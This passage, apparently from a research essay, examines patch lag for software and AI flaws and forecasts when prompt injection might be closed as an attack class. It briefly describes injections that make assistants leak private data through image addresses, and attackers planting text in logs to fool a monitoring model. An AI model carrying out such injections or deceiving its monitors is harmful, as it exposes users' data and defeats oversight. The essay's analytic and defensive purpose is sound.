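Hosting companies can remove most of the installation time for their own products, and they can also shield their customers' software. React2Shell was a flaw in React, a popular toolkit for building websites, that let attackers run code on a server. Netlify's *ongoing response to react2shell* describes how the company and other hosts blocked the attack for all their customers at once. It says that self-hosted sites without such protection "would almost certainly be compromised within hours" of the first working exploit.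 Netlify sells hosting, and this is its prediction about sites it doesn't run.

There is no sign that central control makes vendors write fixes faster. The image leak and Whisper Leak mostly affected hosted products, and many vendors still took months. Users of a hosted product can't protect themselves by installing anything, so they depend on the vendor's priorities.

### Warning the owners

A 2014 randomised trial on Heartbleed provides the best evidence on any of these factors. Heartbleed was a flaw in OpenSSL, the software that encrypts many websites' connections, that let attackers read private data from a server's memory. Three weeks after it became public, researchers scanned the internet and found 588,686 computers that were still vulnerable. They excluded embedded devices, which owners often couldn't patch, and looked up contact addresses for the remaining networks. They randomly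 divided the contacts into two groups and emailed the first on 28 April and the second on 7 May.

After eight days, 39.5% of the contacts in the first group emailed had started patching, compared with 26.8% of those still waiting for an email. Because contacts were assigned to the groups at random, the emails almost certainly caused the difference, which is about one contact in eight. The emails cost almost nothing to send.

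The trial gives less evidence about how long the effect lasts. Both groups levelled off at around 57% within a couple of weeks of the second set of emails, and by then no unwarned group was left for comparison. The researchers also counted a contact as having started once it had patched a single machine, which is far from patching them all. These owners had already ignored three weeks of news coverage, so they may have been harder to persuade than most.

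The larger problem is reaching the right person. In an experiment on vulnerable web applications published in 2016, only 5.8% of 35,832 reports got through. When an owner read one, the chance of a fix was about 40%. In *Didn't You Hear Me?*, Stock, Pellegrino and colleagues ran a further experiment on more than 24,000 domains to find out why warnings don't work better. They write that earlier trials helped many operators but left the vast majority of systems unpatched. The paper *I believe it's incredibly difficult to fight against this flood of spam* describes past results from changing the sender or the wording as often inconsistent, so neither is a reliable answer.

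A stronger option is to cut off the vulnerable system until its owner fixes it. *Tell Me You Fixed It* (Çetin, Gañán and colleagues, 2019) describes itself as the first study to test this. Anthropic did something similar when it forced old versions of Claude Code to update. Nobody has that power over most MCP servers, which belong to many separate owners.

### Publishing the flaw

Publishing a flaw puts pressure on the vendor to fix it, but it also informs attackers. *An Empirical Analysis of Software Vendors' Patching Behavior* (Arora, Krishnan and colleagues, 2006) studied this pressure using records from CERT/CC and SecurityFocus, a website that collected reports of flaws. It estimated that disclosure made vendors 137% more likely to patch, and that immediate disclosure brought the patch forward by almost 29 days. Vendors also responded faster when a flaw was severe or when CERT/CC handled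 the report.

A later analysis in Shape of Code (2016), a blog on software research, plotted survival curves for flaws from 2001 to 2003 and disputed the popular belief that publicizing flaws makes vendors fix them faster.

Both results could be right. If people publish minor flaws at once but report dangerous ones privately, vendors will fix the dangerous ones first. A plain survival curve will then show faster fixes for private reports, even if publication would have sped up every fix. A statistical model can adjust for severity if the records describe it well, but not for things the records leave out, such as how persistent the reporter was. A randomised trial would settle the question, but few researchers would agree to publish dangerous flaws at random.

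The evidence from disclosure deadlines makes it more likely that publication shortens the lag at least somewhat. Vendors fixed many of the flaws Project Zero reported just before the details were due to be published, and severity can't easily explain such a sharp pattern. AI vendors can respond to publication too, as Google did when it fixed NotebookLM within days of Rehberger's post. Publication works less well when a vendor denies that there is anything to fix, as OpenAI first did with ChatGPT.

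### Patches written by AI

AI agents can now write patches for security flaws, and many of these patches look right at first. *PATCHBENCH* (Shen, Li and colleagues, 2026) tested 11 agents on 213 flaws in 32 real C and C++ projects. Each agent received the code and an input that crashed the program, and had to fix the mistake that caused the crash.

The researchers made the test hard in two ways. They chose flaws in which the mistake was in a different part of the program from the crash, so an agent couldn't simply patch the code that crashed. They also moved each flaw into a newer version of the project and rewrote the code around it to stop agents from repeating a patch they had seen in training. On an older test without that precaution, about a quarter of agents' patches closely resembled the original developer's.

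A patch passed only if the patched program did not crash on other inputs that exploited the same flaw, gave the right output on harmless inputs and passed the project's own tests.

| Agent | Stopped the original crash | Passed every check |
|---|---|---|
| Codex with GPT-5.6 Sol, the best | 97.2% | 59.2% |
| Claude Code with Claude Opus 4.8 | 97.7% | 56.8% |
| Average of all 11 | 83.1% | 45.3% |

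The agents' most common mistake was adding a check where the program crashed without fixing the cause, so a slightly different input could still trigger the flaw. One agent stopped an overflow in nDPI, a tool for analysing network traffic, by deleting the whole feature that contained it. Raising the spending limit from $5 to $25 per flaw increased the best agent's score by only 2.3 percentage points.

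Codex's score of 59.2% is slightly too high. Shen and colleagues read the patches that had passed and found that 7.1% of Codex's left part of the flaw's cause in place, which would lower its score to about 55%. However, they had chosen unusually difficult flaws, and newer models may do better.

Results from real projects look much better. Lbath and colleagues report that only 0.53% of the patches from OpenAI's Defense Factory, a service that fixes flaws for selected partners, had to be withdrawn. But developers usually withdraw a patch because it broke something. A patch that breaks nothing but fixes only part of the flaw could stay in place for years without anyone noticing the remaining flaw, as the failed fixes in Chromium and Firefox did.

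### Is writing or review the slow step?

ZDI's median fix time has not moved, even though agents have been writing fixes for real projects since 2025 and an attempt in PatchBench cost less than $3 on average. This suggests that writing the patch is not the slow step. Maintainers accepted 69% of the patches sent by Trail of Bits' Patch the Planet, according to Lbath and colleagues, but had fixed only 24% of the flaws it reported. A ready-made patch may make a fix more likely, though the programme may also have written patches mainly for projects that were likely to respond.

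At a later step, GitHub, which hosts much of the world's open-source code, publishes advisories about flaws in that code. Once GitHub staff have reviewed an advisory, developers who use the affected component are alerted automatically. *Agents on the Patch Path* (Segal, Segal and colleagues, 2026) found 469 reviewed advisories whose linked code changes showed signs of an AI coding agent, usually a credit to a tool such as Claude or Copilot.

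GitHub took an average of 22.0 days to review these AI-associated advisories and 19.5 days to review others from the same months, a difference that could easily be chance. It reviewed the AI-associated ones 13 days faster on average than advisories from 2022 to 2025, but only because a few of the older ones waited for years. When Segal and colleagues capped every wait at 92 days, the AI-associated group was almost 14 days slower.

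GitHub's delay in reviewing advisories grew for everyone during 2026. The median wait for advisories submitted through projects' own GitHub pages rose from 0.4 days in January to 41.4 days in September. GitHub reviewed 1,560 advisories in May, over five times its usual monthly number, and still fell behind. Because GitHub reviews the advisory and not the patch, these waits don't delay the fix itself. They can delay its installation, since some developers don't hear about a fix until GitHub sends the alert.

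Review therefore looks like the slower step for ordinary code flaws, though no study has timed writing and review separately for the same AI-written patches. PatchBench suggests that two in five patches for difficult flaws are wrong, so maintainers can't skip the review needed to catch them. Many of the delays in AI products had a different cause. Blocking outside images takes little code, but vendors spent months deciding whether the leak was a flaw and what they were willing to give up to stop it.

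### Ranking the factors

The table ranks the factors by how strong the evidence is that they shorten the lag, not by how much they shorten it.

| Factor | Best evidence | Main weakness | Where it applies to agents |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1. Warning owners | Randomised Heartbleed trial | One famous flaw, short follow-up | Self-hosted agents and MCP servers with a reachable owner |
| 2. Protection by default | Use of SameSite before and after browsers made it the default | Only some protections can become defaults | Approval steps, blocked images, restricted internet access |
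| 3. Automatic updates | 8.4 million computers, ten programs | Compares newer versions with older ones | Coding assistants on users' own machines |
| 4. Central control | Histories of hosted products | No comparison group | Hosted assistants, for installation time only |
| 5. Publication and deadlines | Arora and colleagues; Project Zero's record | Conflicting analyses of early data | Flaws and leaks that the vendor knows how to fix |
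| 6. Low compatibility cost | PyTorch's default compared with Office's | Only two cases | Fixes that leave the agent's useful abilities alone |
| 7. Federal mandates | Faster patching of KEV flaws from 2022 to 2024 | No comparison of agencies with other organisations | Agents that US agencies host themselves |
| 8. AI-written patches | PatchBench and accepted patches | No study shows a shorter lag | Code flaws, if maintainers have time to review them |

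Warnings rank first because of the trial's design, although their effect was modest. A vendor that wants the largest effect should choose defaults and automatic updates, which changed most users' behaviour in the SameSite and Windows cases. People who report flaws control neither, so a firm publication date is probably their most useful tool, despite its lower rank.

All eight factors help produce or spread a fix, so they do less for prompt injection as a class, which has only partial fixes. Central control and automatic updates can deliver those quickly, and default settings can limit what an agent may do when an injection succeeds. The best evidence that such limits work comes from browsers. Chrome's Site Isolation keeps websites in separate processes, so that an attack on one can't easily reach the data of another. Lbath and colleagues report that the number of flaws it was meant to contain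 fell from nine to two in six months. Those numbers are small and come from the company that built the protection. Browsers can also tell sites apart far more easily than agents can separate a user's request from a stranger's text.

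## Making a forecast for AI agents

There is enough data on past fix times to forecast how soon a vendor will fix a single flaw. Forecasting when a whole attack class such as prompt injection will close is much harder, because only a few old classes have well-documented lags. Two simple rules produce forecasts of 13% and 58% for the same question.

### A single flaw

Vendors never fix some flaws, and they take anything from days to months over the rest. A forecast can treat the two separately:

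P(fixed by day t) = (1 − p) × F(t)

Here p is the chance that the vendor never fixes the flaw, and F(t) is the share of eventual fixes that arrive by day t. A *lognormal* curve is a sensible choice for F, because fix times can't be negative and a few are far longer than the rest. It needs only a median, m, and a spread, s:

F(t) = Φ(ln(t/m) / s)

Φ(x) is the share of a standard bell curve that lies below x. With a spread of 1 and a median of 60 days, about two thirds of the eventual fixes arrive between day 22 and day 163.

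Suppose p is 20%, the median is 60 days and the spread is 1. For day 90, ln(90/60) is 0.405, and 65.7% of the bell curve lies below that value. Multiplying by 0.8 gives a 53% chance of a fix by day 90.

The forecast should change while the flaw stays open. The initial chance of no fix by day 90 was 47%, made up of a 20% chance that the vendor would never fix the flaw and a 27% chance that it would fix it later. If day 90 passes without a fix, the chance that the vendor will never fix the flaw rises to 42%, and the chance of a fix in the next 90 days is 35%.

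Real fixes arrive less smoothly than this. Vendors fixed many of Project Zero's late flaws just before the details were due to be published. So if the reporter has set a deadline, some of the probability the forecast puts after the deadline belongs in the days before it.

### Values from the AI cases

The image leak and the MCP server flaws give rough values for AI products.

| Case | Never fixed (p) | Median | Spread | Fixed by day 30 | By day 90 | By day 365 |
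|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Illustration above | 20% | 60 days | 1.0 | 20% | 53% | 77% |
| Image leak in assistants | 15% | 70 days | 0.8 | 12% | 53% | 83% |
| Open-source MCP servers | 23% | 23 days | 1.0 (assumed) | 47% | 70% | 77% |

For the image leak, p comes from the two refusals among thirteen reports. The median and spread come from the logarithms of the other eleven fix times, using the latest possible date for each. Vendors had fixed 7 of the 13 (54%) by day 90, but the curve's match with that figure shows only that it fits the data it came from.

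The MCP values are less certain. Maintainers' fixes took 37.3 days on average, and a lognormal curve with a spread of 1 has an average 1.65 times its median, which makes the median 23 days. Counting all 12 open flaws as never fixed probably understates the share that maintainers will fix, and leaving them out of the median probably understates how long fixes take.

The image-leak values mostly reflect how vendors respond to Johann Rehberger, so someone forecasting the response to an unknown researcher should use a higher p and a longer median.

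Whisper Leak can't supply values at all. About 14% of the 28 notified providers had a mitigation after roughly 130 days, and very different assumptions reproduce that figure:

| Assumption | Fixed by day 130 | Fixed within two years |
|---|---|---|
| Most providers will act, slowly (p = 20%, median 325 days) | 14% | 63% |
| Most providers will never act (p = 80%, median 75 days) | 14% | 20% |

Only longer follow-up can distinguish slow providers from unwilling ones. A forecaster with only early data should give both possibilities some weight instead of picking the curve that looks best.

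### Adding installation

For a hosted assistant, the forecast only needs to cover the time until the vendor's fix. For self-hosted software, it also has to cover the time until a given machine runs the fix. The forecaster splits the possible release dates into periods, multiplies the chance of a release in each period by the share of machines that would install the fix in the time left before the forecast's deadline, and adds up the results.

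The table does this for an MCP server flaw. Its installation speeds come from Qualys' 2025 curve for known exploited vulnerabilities, and each release is assumed to come in the middle of its period.

| Fix released | Chance | Days left until day 90 | Installed by then | Chance × installed |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Days 0–30 | 47% | 75 | 76% | 35% |
| Days 31–60 | 17% | 45 | 69% | 12% |
| Days 61–90 | 6% | 15 | 45% | 3% |
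| **Total** | **70%** | | | **50%** |

So there is a 70% chance of a fix by day 90, but only a 50% chance that a given machine is running it by then. Even 50% is optimistic, because it assumes owners install the fix as quickly as they do for flaws under attack, which is unusually fast. With the 159-day half-life for vulnerabilities of all kinds and a constant installation rate, the chance falls to 16%. For self-hosted agents, the choice of installation curve can therefore affect the forecast more than anything the vendor does.

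### Two rules for a whole class

Riley Goodside posted the first prompt injections on 11 September 2022. What is the chance that this class of flaw will be closed by September 2032, with protection on by default in most deployed systems?

One rule uses only the age of the class, now about 4.25 years. It assumes that today is a random moment in the period during which the class stays open. If the class closes by 2032, that period lasts ten years or less, so at least 42.5% of it has already passed. A random moment falls that late with a probability of 1 − 4.25/10, so under this rule the chance of closure by 2032 is about 58%. The astrophysicist J. Richard Gott popularized this style of reasoning in the 1990s.

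The other rule, which Laplace devised in the eighteenth century, uses similar past cases. If something happened in k of n cases, the chance that it will happen in the next one is (k + 1)/(n + 2). None of six older classes (buffer overflows, SQL injection, cross-site scripting, cross-site request forgery, Office macros and pickle files) closed within ten years, so the chance that the next class will is 1/8, or about 13%. The added 1 and 2 keep the estimate from being zero after a short run of failures.

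The rules disagree because they use different evidence. The age rule ignores every other attack class. Applied to the six older classes at the same age, it would have given each a 42.5% chance of lasting beyond ten years, and a 0.6% chance that all six would do so if they were independent. It also gives the same 58% whether "closed" means protection by default or the complete disappearance of the attack, though the second is less likely. Finally, it assumes that today is a random moment in the attack's lifetime, although people tend to ask when a problem will end while it is new and causing trouble.

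Laplace's rule assumes that prompt injection resembles the six classes in every way that matters. It also starts from the view that any long-run closure rate between 0% and 100% is equally likely, which has a large effect with only six cases. Small changes in how those cases are counted matter just as much:

| How the six classes are counted | Closed within ten years | Laplace's rule |
|---|---|---|
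| Pickle measured from 2011 | 0 of 6 | 13% |
| Pickle measured from 2021 | 1 of 6 | 25% |
| The same, with Word's macro warning as protection | 2 of 6 | 38% |

Given the Melissa virus, it is hard to count Word's warning as protection. The starting date for pickle is more debatable, so 13% to 25% is a fair range for this set of classes.

### Famous because they lasted

The six classes are also a biased sample. People still write about SQL injection in 2026 because it still works. A class that vendors fixed within three years would have few studies about it and would be unlikely to appear in a comparison like this one.

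The Smurf attack is one such class. In the late 1990s, attackers sent every machine on a network a message with the victim's address forged as the return address, so that all of the machines replied to the victim at once. In 1999 the internet's standards body changed the recommended default so that routers would stop forwarding messages addressed to a whole network, and the attack is now mostly a textbook example.

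Suppose there were 20 attack classes, 8 of which closed within ten years, and historians remember only the longest-lasting. They might list six classes, none of which closed within ten years. Laplace's rule would then give a forecast of 1/8, or 13%, compared with 9/22, or 41%, if it were applied to all 20. Nobody has counted the forgotten classes, so the size of the correction needed is unknown.

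The bias is smaller than that example implies, because prompt injection isn't a typical new class either. It has stayed open for more than four years while hundreds of people tried to stop it, so it can't be among the classes that closed fastest. A better reference class would contain every attack that was prominent about four years after its publication, drawn from textbooks and rankings of that time rather than chosen in hindsight. Until someone compiles it, a forecaster should choose an estimate above 13% but below 41%.

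### Would better AI close the class sooner?

Vendors now use AI models to attack their own agents, then train the agents on the results. Anthropic's computer-use agents became much harder to break during 2026. AI can also make defences outside the model easier to build, for instance by drafting the rules that a design such as CaMeL needs for each task. Because vendors host the agents, they can deliver any improvement within days. None of the six older classes had all these advantages, and nearly six years remain until September 2032.

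However, attackers benefit from better AI too. Lbath and colleagues estimate that open-weight models, which anyone can download and run without the developer's controls, trail closed models by about eight months on twelve security benchmarks. They cite an Anthropic comparison in which the open-weight model GLM 5.3 produced complete exploits in 12% of 410 attempts, compared with 14% for Claude Mythos Preview. Those tests concerned ordinary software flaws, but a model that is good at finding them is probably also useful for writing injections. Attackers can also mislead defensive models, as in one study where text they had placed in a system's logs fooled the model monitoring those logs.

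Companies are also giving agents more to do. A vendor might make today's browser agent nearly immune and then release one that manages the user's bank account and negotiates with other agents. "Most deployed systems" in 2032 will largely be products that don't exist yet, and the image leak showed how easily old mistakes reappear in new products.

On balance, faster AI progress makes closure more likely, because defenders can practise against their own systems without limit and the hosted products with the most users can change quickly. It also makes any forecast for 2032 less certain, which is a reason to avoid probabilities close to 0% or 100%.

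### How earlier forecasts did

The NCSC and OpenAI have both publicly predicted that prompt injection may never be fully solved, but neither gave a date or a probability, so nobody can score their predictions.

Forecasts of the number of CVE records have a track record. FIRST, a non-profit association of incident response teams, publishes one every year. BetaNews' *Record-breaking number of vulnerabilities predicted for 2025* (2025) quotes the head of FIRST's forecasting team, Éireann Leverett, saying that the number of reported flaws was "accelerating". Computer Weekly reports that the total for 2025 passed the top of FIRST's range on 31 December and ended at 49,972. The result should ideally be near the middle of the range, so the article's description of the forecast as "bang on" is generous. FIRST then changed its method to allow ranges that extend further above the median than below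 it.

In February, Infosecurity Magazine's *FIRST Forecasts Record-Breaking 50,000+ CVEs in 2026* (2026) reported that FIRST predicted a median of 59,427 CVE records for 2026, with a 90% range from 30,012 to 117,673. The monthly counts in Epoch AI's *Cyber vulnerabilities* (2026) add up to 109,348 by 5 December. If December matches November, the year will end near 123,000, above the predicted range even though the top of that range was almost four times the bottom.

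Updating the forecast in the spring helped little. In *CVE 2026 Half-Year Forecast Update*, Gamblin (2026) fitted a new model to daily CVE counts through April and projected 65,632 CVEs for the year.

| Month in 2026 | Gamblin's projection, made in May | Epoch AI's count | Count ÷ projection |
|---|---|---|---|
| May | 5,326 | 6,824 | 1.3 |
| July | 5,761 | 9,756 | 1.7 |
| September | 5,736 | 14,922 | 2.6 |
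| November | 5,593 | 17,223 | 3.1 |

Gamblin, who co-wrote FIRST's forecast, had good reasons to expect a plateau. Most of the growth up to April came from GitHub and VulnCheck, which had expanded their cataloguing, partly to give CVE numbers to flaws that were already public. He said the model assumed current conditions would continue. He expected AI to become important in the second half of the year, but a model trained on past counts could not include that expectation.

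FIRST's longer forecasts became outdated even sooner. SecureWorld's *FIRST Forecast* gives medians of 51,018 records for 2027 and 53,289 for 2028, with an upper bound near 193,000 by 2028. At November's pace, 2027 alone would bring about 207,000. The surge could also end. Lbath and colleagues describe a scenario in which the number of records crediting AI, which has been growing almost ninefold a year, peaks and then halves every 10 to 24 months. They base the timing of the peak on three practitioners' opinions, and the records show no sign of it so far.

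Fix times could also depart suddenly from a steady trend. ZDI's median fix time has barely moved in a decade, but CVE counts also grew fairly steadily until this year. A forecaster should therefore give perhaps four fifths of the weight to a lognormal curve fitted to past fixes, and the rest to much faster and much slower outcomes.

### Questions with clear answers

People can also easily disagree about the outcome of a CVE forecast, because sources report different counts. Cornelißen (2026), in *100.000 CVEs*, notes that VulnCheck counted 100,222 records for the year on the afternoon of 13 November, while CVE.ICU had 97,664 the next morning. A bet on whether the total would pass 100,000 by 13 November would have had a different winner depending on which count was used. For 2025, FIRST gives a total of 49,972, CVE.ICU 48,150 and Epoch AI 47,801.

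Even the forecast can be ambiguous. Gamblin counted 20,293 records in the first four months of 2026 and found this 46% higher than expected from a February forecast of 43,757 for the year. But FIRST's published median forecast was 59,427, and his count was almost exactly on pace for that.

Resolution criteria, the rules for deciding whether a forecast came true, should name one source and the date to check it. They also need a rule for missing data, since a flaw with no recorded patch date may still have a patch. A question about whether an attack or a patch came first needs a rule for ties. Bonhomme and Dulaunoy left the order undecided when both fell on the same day and at least one had no recorded time.

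"Will prompt injection be solved by 2032?" is too vague to settle because it doesn't define "solved" or specify which agents count and who tests them. A better question is "By 11 September 2032, will a government institute or a peer-reviewed study have tested the five most-used AI agents and found that attackers break fewer than 1% of scenarios on at least three of them?" The agents would run in their default settings, and attackers would adapt their methods and get 100 attempts per scenario. Each agent would need at least 300 scenarios, because a smaller test with no successful attacks would still be consistent with a rate above 1%. If nobody publishes such a test by the deadline, the answer is no.

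These criteria have a cost. They replace "most deployed systems" with three popular products, and agents could become safe without anyone running the test.

### Scoring

The *Brier score*, which the meteorologist Glenn Brier proposed in 1950 for weather forecasts, is the squared difference between the forecast probability and the outcome, where the outcome is 1 if the event happens and 0 if it doesn't. Lower scores are better, and a forecaster who always says 50% scores 0.25.

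| Forecast of closure by 2032 | Score if closed | Score if still open |
|---|---|---|
| 58%, from the age rule | 0.18 | 0.34 |
| 13%, from Laplace's rule | 0.76 | 0.02 |

Forecasters get the best expected score by reporting the probability they believe. Someone who believes the chance is 30% can expect a score of 0.21 by saying 30%, but a worse score of 0.25 by saying 10% to sound decisive (0.3 × 0.9² + 0.7 × 0.1²).

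One question can't show which rule is better, because unlikely events sometimes happen. Forecasts about individual flaws are a much better test of skill. A company that uses 50 AI products could estimate the chance that each flaw it hears about will be fixed within 90 days, and have dozens of scores within a year. It should compare its average score with the one it would have earned by forecasting the same base rate every time, such as the 53% above.

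### Six forecasts for 2027 to 2032

| Deadline | Event | Probability |
|---|---|---|
| 31 December 2027 | Microsoft, including GitHub, confirms a new case in which an injection makes one of its AI assistants leak private data through an image address | 85% |
| 31 December 2027 | The median time from report to release for fixed flaws in ZDI's 2027 advisories exceeds 120 days, read on 31 January 2028 | 30% |
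| 30 June 2028 | Vendors fixed at least half of the AI flaws that Embrace The Red lists as reported in 2027 within 90 days; void if it lists fewer than ten | 65% |
| 31 December 2028 | CISA adds to its KEV list, after 1 January 2027, a flaw whose CVE record describes it as prompt injection | 60% |
| 31 December 2029 | A system card from Anthropic, OpenAI or Google reports that its strongest adaptive attacker, with at least 100 attempts per scenario, broke fewer than 5% of at least 40 coding scenarios with safeguards on | 65% |
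| 11 September 2032 | Prompt injection is closed, by the test described above | 30% |

Even if all six probabilities are exactly right, their expected average score is 0.21, only slightly better than forecasting 50% every time. A sudden advance in AI attacks could also make several of the forecasts wrong at once.

Researchers found the image leak in a Microsoft product in each of the four years from 2023 to 2026, so Laplace's rule gives a 5/6 chance, or 83%, that they will find it in one again in 2027. Better search tools raise that chance, while a protection shared by all of Microsoft's assistants would lower it.

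**ZDI's median** was between 96 and 119 days in every year from 2016 to 2026, so Laplace's rule gives a probability of 1/13, or 8%, that a year's median will exceed 120 days. The probability should be much higher than that because the surge of reports from late 2026 will enter the statistics in 2027, and the latest quarter's median was 148 days, though it was based on only 28 fixes. The main reason to keep the probability below 50% is ZDI's 120-day deadline.

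The image-leak curve gives each flaw a 53% chance of being fixed within 90 days. Published cases tend to be ones that were fixed quickly, which raises the probability for the group, but a single vendor that ignored several reports could reverse the result.

**The KEV list.** Attackers have more reason to use prompt injection as agents gain access to money and passwords. Many of these flaws are in hosted products, which lowers the probability, because CISA's list tells agencies what to fix and agencies have nothing to install when a vendor repairs its own servers. Whoever writes the CVE record may also classify a prompt injection flaw as something else, such as command injection.

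In the coding test, Anthropic's strongest attacker still broke 36 of 40 scenarios in September 2026 with filters on, but every success was against an older fallback model. Replacing that model could quickly lower the number. But developers keep building stronger attackers, and the criterion always uses the strongest one in the report. A company could also stop publishing the test, which would count as a failure.

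The six older classes suggest a 13% to 25% chance of closure by 2032, and correcting for forgotten classes raises that somewhat. The lack of any complete remedy lowers the estimate, but the test requires only that attacks rarely succeed, which training and limits on agents might achieve without one. Fast AI progress and hosted updates raise the estimate again, though the possibility that nobody runs a suitable test offsets part of that increase. If the test required guaranteed protection against every injection, the estimate would be far lower, perhaps 5%.

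The 30% estimate should fall if years pass without progress. The age rule's estimate would drop from 58% now to 38% in December 2028 and 18% in December 2030. A forecaster should lower the 30% less if independent tests show attacks becoming rare, and more if each new kind of agent starts out as vulnerable as the last.
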